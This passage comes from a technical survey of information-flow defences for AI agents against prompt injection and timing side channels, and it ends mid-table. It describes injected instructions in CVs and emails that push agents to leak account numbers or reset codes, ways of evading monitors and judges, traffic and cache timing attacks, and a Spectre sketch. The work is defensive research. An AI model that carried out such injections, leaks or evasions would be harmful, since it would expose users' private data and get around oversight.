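A journalist who knows how the agent works can infer from its silence that the date has changed. CaMeL's skipped branches leak in the same way, because a secret again determines whether a value gets a public label. Under the usual rules, the wrapper's decision would need the join of the labels of all the documents it examined, which is the strict label the method was supposed to avoid.

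Untrusted documents can also influence the decision. Siddiqui and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker can add distracting text that prevents the wrapper from finding a less strict label. The agent then cannot use the answer in a call that requires trusted data.

### Masking parts of the history

*RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) applies a similar idea to tool calls. Before the agent's next step, a screener selects the relevant regions of the conversation. RTBAS masks the rest and propagates only the labels of the selected regions. If the resulting call would violate a policy, the agent asks the user to confirm it. RTBAS needs one screening pass, whereas Zhong and colleagues estimate that the method of Siddiqui and colleagues needs 16 to 64 extra model calls for a typical set of four to six labels.

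One version of the screener uses a second language model to judge relevance. The other uses *attention*, the weights with which a model draws on earlier tokens (words or pieces of words). A small open model processes the conversation and the call. Each input token's score measures how strongly the attention to it affects the model's prediction of the call. A region's score is its highest token score divided by the highest token score in the whole input. A trained network uses these region scores to pick the relevant regions.

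Zhong and colleagues compared these scores with known dependencies in 3,424 pairs of inputs and tool calls. Between 74% and 86% of unrelated inputs scored below 0.2, but so did 14% of the real dependencies in calls by GPT-4o and 44% of those in calls by Claude. A cut-off at 0.2 would therefore have dropped many labels from inputs that the calls depended on.

On AgentDojo, RTBAS stopped every attack that violated its policies and lost about 2% of task completion under attack. In a separate test of accidental leaks, it allowed the same calls without confirmation as an ideal screener would on all but one task. These results measure the screeners' accuracy on particular inputs and do not bound what an attacker could achieve.

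Masking removes an attacker's text from the context, but only after the screener has processed it, so the text can still affect what else is masked. Suppose the user says to pay an invoice only if it is under $100, and a stranger's email causes the screener to mask that condition as irrelevant. The planner then receives a trusted request without the condition, and the payment gets a trusted label. With k regions, the screener has 2^k possible selections, so its selection can carry up to k bits at each step.

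### Scoring how strongly a span affects the output

*Geometric Information Flow*, or GIF, assigns a number to each span of text. Štorek, Holzer and colleagues (2026), in *GIF*, start from the lists of numbers, called embeddings, that represent tokens inside a model. They imagine adding a little random noise to a span's embeddings and ask how much the next token would reveal about the noise. If the noise has variance τ, then

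```
M          =  Jᵀ Wᵀ (diag(p) − p pᵀ) W J
influence  =  sum of the diagonal entries of M
flow       ≤  (τ / 2) × influence  +  terms that shrink faster than τ
```

Here J describes how small changes to the span affect the model's final internal state, W turns that state into a score for each possible next token, and p contains the resulting probabilities. Calculating M in full takes too much computation for large models, so the system estimates the influence by sending a few random test vectors through the model.

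In one example, a job applicant's CV contains an instruction to recommend the applicant at a salary of $200,000, and the agent complies. GIF attributes 82 bits of flow to the injected text, 27 to the employer's hiring criteria and 16 to the rest. The system then gives the highest-scoring spans to another language model, which allows or denies the action.

Štorek and colleagues tested the scores on six open models and three benchmarks: AgentDojo, MSB for tool attacks, and AgentDAM for privacy in web tasks. They measured what share of the 50 highest-scoring tokens belonged to known injections or private data. The table shows how well this share separated runs with violations from runs without them, where 0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect. The RTBAS figures are for a reimplementation of its attention method.

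| | AgentDojo | MSB | AgentDAM |
|---|---|---|---|
| GIF | 0.91 | 0.92 | 0.75 |
| RTBAS attention | 0.84 | 0.76 | 0.57 |

A language model judging only the top one to three spans did 0.97 to 1.22 times as well as the same model reading the whole run. On AgentDojo and MSB, showing it only the top span used about a third as many tokens.

The inequality has a proof checked in Lean, but it covers only very small noise around one fixed prompt. Replacing a stranger's email with a different one is not a small change to its embeddings, so the theorem does not bound the effect the other email could have had on the model.

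### Why a score near zero proves little

Xu and colleagues prove that a span can have almost no local influence and still decide the output. Suppose a model chooses between "approve" and "reject". The score for "approve" is 20u, where u comes from an email, and the score for "reject" is always 0. If u = 1, the model approves with near certainty and the email's local influence is about 0.0000008. If the email had set u to −1, the model would have rejected with the same certainty.

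The influence is tiny because the model is so confident that a small nudge hardly changes the probabilities. Confident outputs are common. For one in five outputs in the study, Qwen3-8B assigned other tokens less than 1% of the probability on average.

Attention can fail similarly. In another construction by Xu and colleagues, the model gives a span an attention weight of 0.000000002, but different content there would have raised the weight to nearly 1 and changed the output. They compare this to an implicit flow through a branch the program did not take.

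Štorek and colleagues describe an agent that turns private notes into a public comment and leaves out a neighbour's address. GIF gives the address a flow of zero, and they present this as evidence that GIF can certify that nothing flowed. But the score does not show that the comment would have been the same with any other address.

Removing a span and checking whether the output changes can instead miss influence when other spans repeat the same content. If an attacker sends the same false price in three emails, removing any one of them leaves the output unchanged. Siddiqui and colleagues' wrapper avoids this problem when all the copies are untrusted, because it removes all untrusted documents together.

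### Choosing a miss rate in advance

Xu and colleagues' tool, Sightline, learns from labelled examples which attention patterns indicate that an output used an input. It then takes one real dependency from each of n groups of calls in separate calibration data and sets a threshold at the k-th lowest of their scores, where k is α(n + 1) rounded down and α is the target miss rate. A real dependency in a new group then scores below the threshold with probability at most α, provided the new group comes from the same population as the others.

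Xu and colleagues compared several methods on calls from programs not used in training. The left column of figures shows how many unnecessary labels each method removed when calibrated to miss 1% of real dependencies. The right column shows how well each method's scores separated real from unnecessary dependencies on the most confident fifth of outputs, on the same scale as before. The ranges are across four models.

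| | Unnecessary labels removed | Separation on confident outputs |
|---|---|---|
| Sightline | 44–66% | 0.91–0.96 |
| RTBAS attention | 15–29% | 0.83–0.89 |
| GIF, summed over 32 tokens | 1–12% | 0.63–0.75 |

In an agent, Sightline removed about half of the unnecessary labels, and no attack call passed the integrity policy. But its guarantee holds only on average, over calls like those in the calibration data, so it does not cover an attacker who searches for inputs that the tool misses.

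Misses also accumulate. If each call has a 1% chance of a miss and misses are independent, an agent that makes 50 calls with real dependencies has about a 39% chance of at least one miss. Small effects can add up too. Suppose a secret bit makes a model use a certain word in 55% of replies instead of 45%. One reply reveals less than a hundredth of a bit, but an observer who counts the word over 400 replies can guess the secret correctly about 98% of the time.

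### Running the agent without the user's task

Zhu, Yang and colleagues (2025), in *MELON*, look for actions that do not depend on what the user asked. Their defence runs a second copy of the agent at each step:

1. The original agent proposes its next tool calls, and MELON holds them back.
2. The copy receives the same tool results, but a neutral request to summarise them and follow any instructions they contain replaces the user's task.
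3. MELON saves every tool call that the copy proposes, in case the original agent obeys the same injection later.
4. If a call from the original agent closely resembles a saved one, MELON stops the run.

The comparison converts each call to a short description and measures how similar the descriptions are. For emails, it uses only the recipient, so two emails to the same recipient match even if their wording differs.

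Zhu and colleagues tested MELON on AgentDojo's 629 security cases, using four styles of injection and three models. The table gives the results for GPT-4o.

| | No defence | MELON |
|---|---|---|
| Attack success, average of four styles | 16.1% | 0.2% |
| Attack success, most effective style | 51.0% | 1.0% |
| Tasks completed, no attack | 80.4% | 68.0% |
| Tasks completed, most effective style | 54.1% | 32.9% |

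When there was no attack, MELON wrongly stopped nine of the 97 user tasks. All nine asked the agent to follow instructions from an outside source, such as a to-do list on a website, so the agent's tool calls depended mostly on that source even though the user wanted the agent to make them.

Across the three models, 66 attacks of the most effective style escaped detection. In 73% of these, the injection achieved its goal through the agent's text, for example by persuading the user to buy something expensive. MELON compares only tool calls, so it does not check the agent's text.

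The paper calls MELON provable because of a bound for a version with n different neutral requests. If the average similarity for attacks is μ and the alarm threshold is θ, then

```
chance of missing an attack  ≤  exp(−2n(μ − θ)²)      if μ > θ
```

With μ = 0.7, θ = 0.5 and n = 100, the bound is about 0.03%. It also requires the n comparisons to be independent. However, the attacker writes the injection and can try to write one that puts μ below θ. If the attacker succeeds, adding more neutral requests makes a miss more likely.

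MELON's test also differs from noninterference in that it changes the user's task and keeps the stranger's text fixed, instead of the other way around. It may therefore miss an injection such as "if the user wants to pay this bill, use the following account", because the copy isn't asked to pay anything and nothing prompts it to propose the same payment.

### A separate model that approves releases

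FlowSeal, the September 2026 system in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, combines labels with a model's judgement. Private records are labelled with their owners. Ordinary code outside the agent's model intercepts every call that writes or shares data, tracks which records may have contributed to that data, and checks the destination. When private records might reach someone not entitled to them, a separate model call compares the records with the proposed output and decides whether to release it.

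This model is not given the conversation, so an outsider cannot try to persuade it directly. A judge that shares the agent's context can be misled by the same messages as the agent. In one attack, an outsider invites the agent to fill in its part of a shared page, and the agent treats this as ordinary teamwork instead of a request for private information. The attack obtained 52.2% of the private items from an agent with an earlier defence and 0.5% from one with FlowSeal. Across the eight attacks tested, the agent with FlowSeal leaked between 0% and 3.3% of the items. It completed 72.4% of ordinary tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best alternative.

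The accompanying proof covers the labels and the interception. It shows that labelled data cannot move to a less protected destination without passing the release check. The judge's accuracy has to be measured instead. The threat model excludes prompt injection.

A judge can leak information even when it recognises every secret. If an outsider asks the agent to write on a shared page that a patient has asthma, and the judge blocks true statements but allows false ones, the missing statement confirms the diagnosis. The outsider can also keep rewording a request until the agent produces an output that the judge misreads. Christodorescu and colleagues warn that attackers can exploit the 1% of cases that a 99% accurate monitor gets wrong. If attempts are independent, an attacker would have a 63% chance of getting past such a monitor within 100 tries and a 95% chance within 300.

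### What repeated runs can show

Since none of these estimates proves noninterference, one might test for it directly. Each test draws a task and two versions of the forbidden data at random, runs a deterministic agent on both, and compares everything the observer sees. Let r be the probability that such a test finds a difference. All n independent tests come out clean with probability (1 − r)ⁿ, and

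```
(1 − r)ⁿ  ≥  0.05      means      r  ≤  1 − 0.05^(1/n)  ≈  3/n
```

After n clean tests, the rate is therefore at most about 3/n, with 95% confidence. Xu and colleagues use this kind of bound for a different property. They planted unique values in prompts and kept the 100 to 137 cases per model in which the value appeared in the output. Sightline detected the dependency every time, so its miss rate in such cases is below 3% for each model.

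The formula assumes that the tests are independent. AgentDojo's 629 cases reuse a much smaller set of tasks and attacker goals, so 629 failed attacks are weaker evidence than the formula's 0.5% suggests.

If the agent samples its replies, a test for influence must compare how often a call occurs over many runs instead of comparing single runs. If changing the secret moves the probability of a call from 50% to 51%, a test with a 5% false alarm rate needs about 39,000 runs with each version of the secret to have an 80% chance of detecting the change.

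Random tests, however many, do not cover inputs that an attacker chooses. Suppose an agent misbehaves only when an email contains a particular ten-digit code. A million tests with random codes will almost certainly find nothing. The bound of three in a million will be correct for random emails, but an attacker who knows the code will succeed every time.

### Choosing the inputs before reading them

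Siddiqui and colleagues mention a simpler method for cases where the label that the answer must have is known from the start. The system skips the search and gives the model only documents that may flow to that label:

```
inputs = documents whose labels may flow to the required label
reply  = model(question, inputs)
```

Noninterference then follows by the same argument as for f-secure, without any estimate of influence, as long as forbidden data cannot affect which permitted documents the model receives. The system therefore has to remove forbidden items before ranking, because they could otherwise push permitted ones out of the results, as in f-secure's email search.

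When the system does not know in advance who will read the answer, it can always produce one answer for each label. *Secure multi-execution*, a technique from 2010, does this for ordinary programs. It runs the program once per security level, replacing data above that level with dummy values. In the launch example, the agent would write one answer for the journalist using only the announcement and another for employees using both documents. The journalist would then receive "3 May" whatever the memo contained, even if the launch had moved to June.

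## Timing and traffic: what an observer learns from when an agent acts

In the launch example, suppose secure multi-execution finishes the employees' answer before starting the journalist's. If a memo that moves the launch makes the employees' answer take longer to write, the journalist's answer arrives later. This delay violates noninterference even though the text of the journalist's answer satisfies it.

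Most definitions of noninterference leave out timing. The standard formula in a lecture by Stephen Chong of Harvard University compares the values in memory when two runs end, however long each run took. The theorem of Garby and colleagues compares results, and f-secure's definition compares sequences of steps. *PerMIT* states that timing is out of scope. Its planner has no clock, so delays cannot influence it directly, but an outsider can still time the agent.

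### Adding times to the definition

An observer with a clock sees a list of events e, each with a time t, rounded to the precision of the clock. *Timing-sensitive noninterference* requires the whole list to have the same distribution in both runs:

```
μ ≈ ν   implies   Pr[(e₁,t₁), ..., (eₙ,tₙ) | μ] = Pr[(e₁,t₁), ..., (eₙ,tₙ) | ν]
```

This definition also forbids the termination leaks that CaMeL's repaired monitor would still allow, because a reply that never arrives is the extreme case of a late reply.

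Before noninterference was defined, Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, asked how a customer can run someone else's program on private data without the program passing that data to its owner. Besides files and messages, Lampson's list of leaks includes the bill for the service, the time it used, and its effect on the speed of other programs. Lampson called a channel *covert* if it was "not intended for information transfer at all". When an agent pays its model provider by the token, its bill can leak information in the same way to whoever receives it.

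*Plugging Side-Channel Leaks with Timing Information Flow Control* (Ford, 2012) proposed giving each message or process a timing label in addition to its content label. An email's content can then be labeled public while its sending time is labeled secret. *Language-based control and mitigation of timing channels* (Zhang, Askarov and Myers, 2012) presents a type system that provably bounds how much a program leaks through timing, under explicit assumptions about the hardware. A similar theorem for an agent would also need assumptions about the servers that run the model.

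### Four steps or six

SPA's checker would accept the following plan, a variation on the earlier one about a medical appointment:

```
record  = tool read_record(day="Friday")
summary = q-llm("Summarize the appointment", record)
tool save_private_note(text=summary)
condition record.department == "oncology":
    details = q-llm("List what to bring", record)
    tool save_private_note(text=details)
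tool send_email(to="office@example.com", body="I am away on Friday.")
```

The email is outside the branch and its fixed text contains nothing from the record, so its input label is public. But the agent sends it as the fourth step for most appointments and as the sixth for an oncology appointment. If the agent always starts at nine o'clock and each step takes two seconds, the email leaves 8 or 12 seconds after nine. If both cases were equally likely beforehand, the office learns one bit from the email's timing.

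Here the planner could remove the leak with no downside by sending the email first. SPA's rules allow either order, so nothing makes the planner choose the safe one. This fix isn't possible when the agent has to read the secret before it can act, such as when it must check a private calendar before answering an invitation.

### Recovering the bit from noisy times

Suppose the mail server adds a random delay that averages 20 seconds and follows a bell curve with a standard deviation of 4 seconds. The email now arrives after 28 or 32 seconds on average, and the two distributions overlap heavily. The office's best guess after one email is "oncology" if it took more than 30 seconds. If the appointment recurs every week in the same department, the office can average the times. With d for the difference in seconds, σ for the standard deviation and Φ for the cumulative normal distribution,

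```
chance of a correct guess after n emails  =  Φ( d√n / 2σ )
```

| Emails observed | Chance of a correct guess |
|---|---|
| 1 | 69% |
| 4 | 84% |
| 9 | 93% |
| 16 | 98% |
| 25 | 99.4% |

Doubling the spread of the delays only quadruples the number of emails the office needs. Lampson made the general point that, with a suitable encoding, any nonzero effect, however small, is enough to send information reliably through a noisy channel. Averaging requires a fresh delay for each email, because further emails would add no information if the server reused the same delay every week.

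*An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) argues that any claim about a covert channel should therefore state the channel's capacity. A one-bit channel that is wrong with probability a has capacity 1 − H(a), where H(a) is the Shannon entropy of an event with that probability. The single guess above is wrong 31% of the time, so the capacity is about 0.11 bits per email.

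### What the agent's own steps reveal

An agent's pauses and bursts of traffic depend on which tools it calls and how often. In *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis*, Zhang, Deng and colleagues (2025) recorded encrypted traffic between users and 50 agents for tasks such as searching the literature, drawing diagrams and running code. A classifier given only the size and timing of the traffic identified the agent 86.7% of the time.

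The agents a person uses also hint at that person's job. Given three guesses among 12 groups of occupations, the method was right for 73.9% of simulated users in jobs where language models are most useful and 58.9% across all jobs. It was right for 69.1% of 49 real participants. Three blind guesses among 12 equal groups would be right 25% of the time.

Teams of agents leave similar traces. In *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks*, Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues (2026) recorded 2,838 runs by teams of two to five agents on ten kinds of task. With all packet-size and data-volume features removed, an observer could still identify the kind of task from the rhythm of the traffic in 54% to 59% of cases, compared with 10% by chance. With sizes included, the figure rose to about 85%. Padding every packet to the same length would therefore not hide what the agents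 were doing.

These classifiers had to choose from a known list of tasks, and all the agents ran the same small model. When the researchers trained a classifier on teams with one communication structure and tested it on teams with a different one, accuracy fell from 83% to 52%.

Running the model on one's own computer hides only some of this traffic. Jeong, Teymoorianfard and colleagues found in *Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents* (2025) that a research agent visits 70 to 140 web domains per request. They used the addresses and times of those visits to recover over 73% of the functional and domain knowledge in users' prompts, by their own measure of similarity.

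*Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026) points out that a website can also actively probe for private information, because what an agent reads on a page, combined with its user's private context, influences which pages it requests next. A monitor that enforces permitted flow would stop this by blocking requests to outside sites once the context is secret. It would not stop an eavesdropper from counting the agent's calls to its model provider, because those calls leave the computer without passing through any tool policy.

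### What model serving reveals

Providers usually stream a reply a few tokens at a time. Encryption hides the text but hardly changes its length, so the size of each packet reveals roughly how much text it contains. McDonald and Bar Or (2025), in *Whisper Leak*, tested whether an eavesdropper could recognise a topic this way. They sent 28 models many phrasings of a question about the legality of money laundering, mixed with 11,716 unrelated questions, and trained classifiers on the sizes and timing of the encrypted packets. For 17 models, the classifiers scored above 98% on a measure that combines how many target conversations they find with how few false alarms they raise.

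Most of the information came from packet sizes. For Mistral Large, sizes alone gave a score of 100% and times alone at most 64%. For Google's Gemini 1.5 Flash, which sent about 55 tokens at once, times were slightly more informative than sizes, although neither gave a score above 83%. McDonald and Bar Or also projected that an eavesdropper could find some target conversations without false alarms even if other conversations outnumbered them 10,000 to one, but their test data were much too small to check this directly.

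The two Microsoft researchers began notifying providers in June 2025. OpenAI, xAI, Mistral and Microsoft deployed fixes between August and October, while other providers declined or did not answer. All the measurements predate the fixes.

Timing leaks more information when the provider speeds up easy text. In *speculative decoding*, a small model drafts several tokens and the large model checks them all at once. If the large model accepts the draft, the reply advances by several tokens, but if it rejects a token, drafting restarts from there. Carlini and Nasr (2024) found in *Remote Timing Attacks on Efficient Language Model Inference* that the April 2024 version of GPT-4 Turbo answered easy requests twice as fast as hard ones, while the June 2023 version of GPT-4 showed no difference.

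On open-source systems with such methods, Carlini and Nasr could tell medical conversations from programming ones in 89.5% to 99.8% of cases after several exchanges. On the ChatGPT website, using packet sizes as well, they were right about 80% of the time from a single message. By combining the timings of 100 variations on a request, they could identify without error which of 1,000 questions it contained. A classifier trained on GPT-3.5 fell to chance within about a month, probably because OpenAI had changed how it served the model. Carlini and Nasr informed OpenAI and Anthropic of the attack in early 2024.

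The same mechanism also matters for integrity, because it lets untrusted text affect when an agent acts. *Speedbumps* (2026) studies text that slows the reply by making speculative decoding less efficient.

### What other users of the same servers can learn

Many providers save the results of processing a prompt so that the next prompt with the same beginning takes less time. Agents benefit greatly from this *prompt caching* because they resend their growing conversation at every step. If customers share a cache, however, one customer can infer from a fast response that another has recently sent the same text.

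Gu, Li and colleagues (2025) tested 17 providers in autumn 2024 for *Auditing Prompt Caching in Language Model APIs*. Their audit resembles a direct test of timing-sensitive noninterference. One account sent a prompt, another sent a prompt with the same beginning, and the researchers compared the second account's response times with those for fresh random prompts. If the first account's prompts had no effect on the second, the two sets of times would follow the same distribution. The researchers took 250 measurements for each set and counted a difference as evidence of an effect only if chance would produce one that large less than once in a hundred million tests.

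The audit detected caching at eight providers, and at seven of them unrelated customers shared a cache. A single response time was a fairly good sign of whether a prompt was cached, but the researchers could not reconstruct unknown prompts word by word. The audit also missed a cache at DeepSeek, which openly reported cache use but had no measurable difference in response times. Failing to detect a cache therefore does not prove that none exists.

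At least five providers made changes after Gu and colleagues contacted them. The researchers recommend a separate cache for each user, or delaying fast responses to look like slow ones. But if a company runs one agent for thousands of customers through a single account, the provider counts them all as one user, and their prompts may still share a cache.

Sharing hardware creates leaks even when programs share no data. *PolicySniff* (2026) describes a program that runs on the same graphics processor as an agent's model. By timing the processor, the program identified which approval rule the agent was following, even though the agent's task was the same under each rule. This is Lampson's leak through system load. *Deterministically Deterring Timing Attacks in Deterland* (Wu and Ford, 2015) describes a system that addresses such leaks in cloud computing. The system gives programs an artificial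 clock that runs the same way every time, so they cannot time other programs on the same hardware, and it paces their output.

### Constant rates, batches and padding

The most direct defence is to send messages at fixed intervals, whether or not any output is ready. Carlini and Nasr propose this for streamed replies, with empty messages to fill the gaps. Sending every 10 milliseconds adds almost no delay but increases traffic by 50% to 300%. Sending every 80 milliseconds increases traffic by less than 10% but delays each token by 4 to 13 milliseconds. An eavesdropper can still see when the stream ends, so the reply must also be padded to hide its length.

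Weaker defenses let an observer learn more. McDonald and Bar Or tested random padding, sending tokens in batches of five, and injecting dummy packets on GPT-4o mini. Each lowered the classifier's score from about 98% to between 93% and 95%. Batching worked much better on most of the other models they tested.

For whole agents, *AgenticOS* (2026) collects outgoing requests into fixed time windows and pads outputs to fixed sizes, but acknowledges that this only narrows covert channels. The number of messages in each window can still vary. *Fingerprinting All AI Cluster I/O Without Mutually Trusted Processors* (2026) calculates that a fast data-centre link can carry up to 625,000 small packets in a 10-millisecond window, so the count alone could encode about 19 bits. It proposes fixing the number and order of packets too.

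Dummy messages work only against observers who cannot recognise them. An eavesdropper cannot tell an encrypted dummy from a real message, but the office in the earlier example would notice an empty email. An agent could also pad every run to six steps. Each dummy step must then take as long as a real one and have no side effects, which rules out dummy payments.

### Predictive mitigation

A fixed schedule wastes time if it is slow and fails if it is too fast. In *Predictive black-box mitigation of timing channels*, Askarov, Zhang and Myers (2010) proposed a compromise in which a *mitigator* between the program and the observer predicts when outputs will be ready and releases them only at the predicted times. As long as the predictions hold, the times reveal nothing new. When an output is late, the observer learns something, and the mitigator switches to a slower schedule.

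In a simple version, the mitigator starts with an interval q and doubles it after every miss. The kth miss cannot happen before q(2ᵏ − 1), so there are at most log₂(T/q + 1) misses by time T. Each can fall on one of at most T/q slots, or not happen at all. The number of possible timing patterns is therefore limited, and

```
leak through timing  ≤  ( log₂(T/q + 1) )²
```

With an initial interval of one second, this comes to about 140 bits in an hour and 269 bits in a day. Without the mitigator, a program that chooses each second whether to send a message could leak 3,600 bits in an hour.

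*Predictive mitigation of timing channels in interactive systems* (Zhang, Askarov and Myers, 2011) extended the method to systems that answer requests, and showed that predictions may use any public information. An agent's mitigator could allow more time for a research report than for a calendar query, provided the observer is allowed to know which one the user requested.

### An agent with no limit on its steps

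Most agents send far fewer messages than a network server does, so the time of a single reply matters more. Suppose a reply may be ready at any moment within an hour. The observer sees either when it arrives or that none has arrived by the end of the hour. The table's upper bound on the leak comes from counting these possible outcomes.

| When trusted code releases the reply | Possible outcomes | Leak at most | Extra delay |
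|---|---|---|---|
| as soon as it is ready, timed to the millisecond | 3,600,001 | 21.8 bits | none |
| at the next multiple of 15 seconds | 241 | 7.9 bits | up to 15 seconds |
| after 15 seconds, 30 seconds, 1 minute, 2 minutes and so on | 9 | 3.2 bits | after the first 15 seconds, less than the run itself took |
| only at the end of the hour | 2 | 1 bit | up to an hour |

A leakage budget that counts a yes-or-no reply as one bit can therefore miss more than 20 bits in its timing.

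If the planner samples its replies and may take any number of steps, no deadline is certain to be long enough, so padding every run to the worst case is impossible. Batching and doubling both still work, but the number of possible release times grows with the length of the run. Random delays need a limit on how much a small change in the input can change the running time. *A Framework for Differential Privacy Against Timing Attacks* (2024) adds them to programs that meet this condition. An agent does not meet it if one more email can make it take fifty more steps.

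A fixed deadline becomes possible again with a cut-off: trusted code holds every finished result until the deadline and stops any run that is not done by then. An agent that satisfies TIPNI, the property proved for LLMbda, still satisfies it with the cut-off. Stopping slow runs can only lower the probability of each visible result, so a shared upper bound ω for two secrets remains an upper bound. Every result appears at the same moment, so the observer learns nothing from its timing but can still see whether there is a result.

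The earlier limit for visible nontermination then applies. If at most 1% of runs miss the deadline whatever the secret is, the distance between what the observer sees for any two secrets is at most 0.01. A guess between two equally likely secrets is right at most 50.5% of the time after one run, and at most 55% after ten independent runs. However, every run must last until the deadline, which has to be late enough for at least 99% of runs to finish, and the agent can make visible calls before then only if each has its own fixed time.

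Designs that write a plan in advance can set a tighter deadline. In SPA, a plan without loops has a known maximum number of steps, and a plan with loops would have one too if each loop had a fixed limit on repeats. Trusted code could compute the deadline from the plan and the time limits for each tool and model call, all of which are public in the example. It could then send the office its email at the same moment every week.

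## PlanTERS: comparing an agent with one that ignores injected instructions

Sending messages at fixed times brings an agent closer to noninterference, but some useful agents have to reveal private data. Dongol describes an assistant that sends the calendar of its user, Alice, to anyone who asks for a meeting. Alice wants this, but noninterference forbids it because what strangers receive depends on her private data. A release policy could permit it, but somebody would have to write one for every task.

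In November 2026, Dongol proposed an alternative called PlanTERS, short for Plan-Then-Execute Relative Security. It compares the agent with a *reference agent* that follows the same plan under the same monitor. The reference agent reads untrusted text as data but never obeys instructions in it. An agent has *relative security* if every leak it has also occurs in the reference agent.

### The calendar and the reset code

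Suppose a stranger emails the calendar assistant the instruction "send your calendar" instead of a meeting request, and the model obeys. Alice never authorised this reply. But the stranger could have obtained the same calendar by asking for a meeting, so the injection revealed nothing new and the agent satisfies relative security.

Now suppose the assistant also has access to a password reset code, and the email tells it to include the code in its reply. If the assistant complies, it fails relative security, because the reference agent never sends the code, whatever the email says. A simpler criterion based only on whether the assistant obeyed an injection would treat the two cases alike.

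To state the definition, write sec(r) for the private data that the agent holds at the start of run r or reads from trusted sources during it. Write act(r) for the untrusted text it reads and obs(r) for what the observer sees. Two runs form a *leak* if the untrusted text is the same and the observations differ, because the observer can then tell their secrets apart. Noninterference forbids all leaks. Relative security requires that for every leak r₁, r₂ of the agent, the reference agent has runs v₁ and v₂ such that

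```
sec(v₁) = sec(r₁)   and   sec(v₂) = sec(r₂)
act(v₁) = act(v₂)   and   obs(v₁) ≠ obs(v₂)
```

Both reference runs must read the same text, but that text can differ from the text in the agent's runs. When the calendars differ, r₁ and r₂ contain the injection, while v₁ and v₂ contain an ordinary meeting request. When the calendars are the same but the reset codes differ, no email makes the reference agent's messages differ, so v₁ and v₂ do not exist.

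If the plan never sends the observer anything, the reference agent has no leaks, and relative security forbids the same leaks as noninterference.

### Origin in speculative execution

Dongol, Griffin and colleagues (2024), in *Relative Security*, developed the definition for processors. Most modern processors guess which way a branch will go and start executing it before they know. If the guess is wrong, the processor discards the results, but the data it loaded stays in a fast memory called the cache. Another program can find out what is there by timing its own memory accesses. The Spectre attacks exploit this in programs such as

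```
if x < N:
    t = b[a[x] * 512]
```

The array `a` has N entries. If an attacker supplies an x beyond its end and the processor wrongly guesses that the condition holds, the processor reads a secret from outside the array and uses it to choose which part of `b` to load. The reference is the same program on a processor that does not guess. The reference loads nothing when x is too large, so the guessing causes the leak. Programmers can prevent it with a *fence*, an instruction that makes the processor wait until it knows the outcome of the branch.

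A variant of this program shows why the reference may use a different attacker input. Suppose the program reads `a[0]` instead of `a[x]`, and N is 2. An attacker who supplies 3 can learn `a[0]` when the processor guesses wrong, but supplying 1 reveals `a[0]` without guessing, so speculation reveals nothing more. Dongol and colleagues point out that an earlier criterion, which required the same input in both cases, rejects this harmless program.

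In PlanTERS, the model that obeys injections corresponds to the processor that guesses, and a monitor that revokes tools serves as the fence.

*Information Security as Strategic (In)effectivity* (Jamroga and Tabatabaei, 2016) had already compared a system with an idealised variant that satisfies noninterference. The real system is acceptable if an attacker can do no more harm in it than in the variant. By this standard, a blog post that mentions a grandmother's maiden name is harmless, but one that mentions a mother's maiden name is dangerous if a bank uses that name to identify customers. This approach requires a definition of harm, whereas relative security considers only what an observer can distinguish.

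### The fence theorem

In PlanTERS, a trusted planner fixes the plan before the agent reads anything untrusted. The attacker then chooses which texts the model treats as instructions, which call each text specifies, and at which steps the model follows them. When the model follows an injected instruction, the agent makes the specified call and then resumes the plan. The call's arguments may contain anything in the agent's memory.

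Dongol illustrates this with an agent that looks up Alice's account number, reads an email and shows her a summary. The email contains an instruction to fetch a web address on the attacker's server with the account number attached. The plan doesn't include fetching anything, so the injected instruction introduces a new leak. If the monitor revokes the fetching tool when the agent reads the email, the monitor refuses the injected call and the agent is relatively secure.

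The fence theorem generalises this example to every plan, under four conditions:

- At the first untrusted read, the monitor revokes every tool that an injection could call.
- No later trusted input restores any of these tools.
- Each injection is a single call, and the agent does not store its result.
- The model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance, so neither secrets nor the monitor's answers affect when it obeys.

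The observer in the theorem sees the contents and order of visible calls but cannot see refusals or time the steps.

The proof compares the agent with the reference agent step by step. Before the first untrusted read, there are no injected instructions to obey, so both take the same steps. Afterwards, the monitor refuses every injected call. A refusal leaves the agent's memory, its place in the plan and the monitor's state unchanged, so the reference agent can wait for the next planned step. Each run of the agent therefore has a matching run of the reference agent with the same secrets, untrusted text and visible calls.

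Leaks return when the conditions don't hold. In one example, an agent handles a private report and an email in each round of a loop, and regains its sending tool with each new report. The previous email is still in the model's context, so the model can follow its instructions and send the new report to the attacker. Starting a fresh model session in every round before restoring the tool prevents this leak. In another example, the injection is a short program that overwrites a variable with a secret. The plan later sends that variable, and the fence permits the call because it is part of the plan.

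The condition about the schedule is hard to justify for a real model, because whether the model obeys an injected instruction may well depend on a secret. The fence blocks injected calls whenever they occur, so the result would probably hold without this condition, but Dongol leaves such models to future work.

The theorem also depends on how the agent is built. For example, a fresh session must erase everything the model has retained from untrusted text. An attack called SpAIware broke this assumption by making ChatGPT save an instruction in its long-term memory, which every later conversation loaded.

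A fence blocks nothing the summarising agent needs, because its plan never fetches web pages. But if the calendar assistant's monitor revoked the sending tool whenever the assistant read an email, the assistant could never answer a meeting request. Dongol equates this kind of fence with the trusted-action policy in FIDES when one label covers the whole context, and that policy blocks useful calls for the same reason.

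### Early, middle and late locks

A plan can also call a tool named Lock, after which the monitor blocks all sending. Dongol compares three positions for this call in a plan that reads a stranger's email and a secret.

| Lock | Order of steps | What an injected message can reveal |
|---|---|---|
| Late | read the email, read the secret, lock | the secret and anything already in memory |
| Middle | read the email, lock, read the secret | anything already in memory |
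| Early | lock, then read the email and the secret | nothing |

The middle lock may not be enough, even though it comes before the secret. The agent may still hold private data from an earlier session, and the model can send that data as soon as it has read the email.

A processor needs a fence only just before the code that would leak, because that code is already in the program. An injection can add a leaking call at any step after the agent reads it, so the lock has to come before the first untrusted read.

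### Approving one exact message

User approval lets an agent send messages after it has read untrusted text. If Alice approves the next message whatever its content, an injection can make the agent use her approval to send private data, and the monitor then blocks the reply she wanted. Approving one exact message is safer, but timing can still leak information.

Suppose the agent has access to the day of Alice's medical appointment, but the plan never sends that information. A stranger's email contains an instruction to send the day of the appointment. Alice approves the reply "Tuesday", and the model follows the stranger's instruction just before the plan sends her reply.

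| Step | Appointment on Friday | Appointment on Tuesday |
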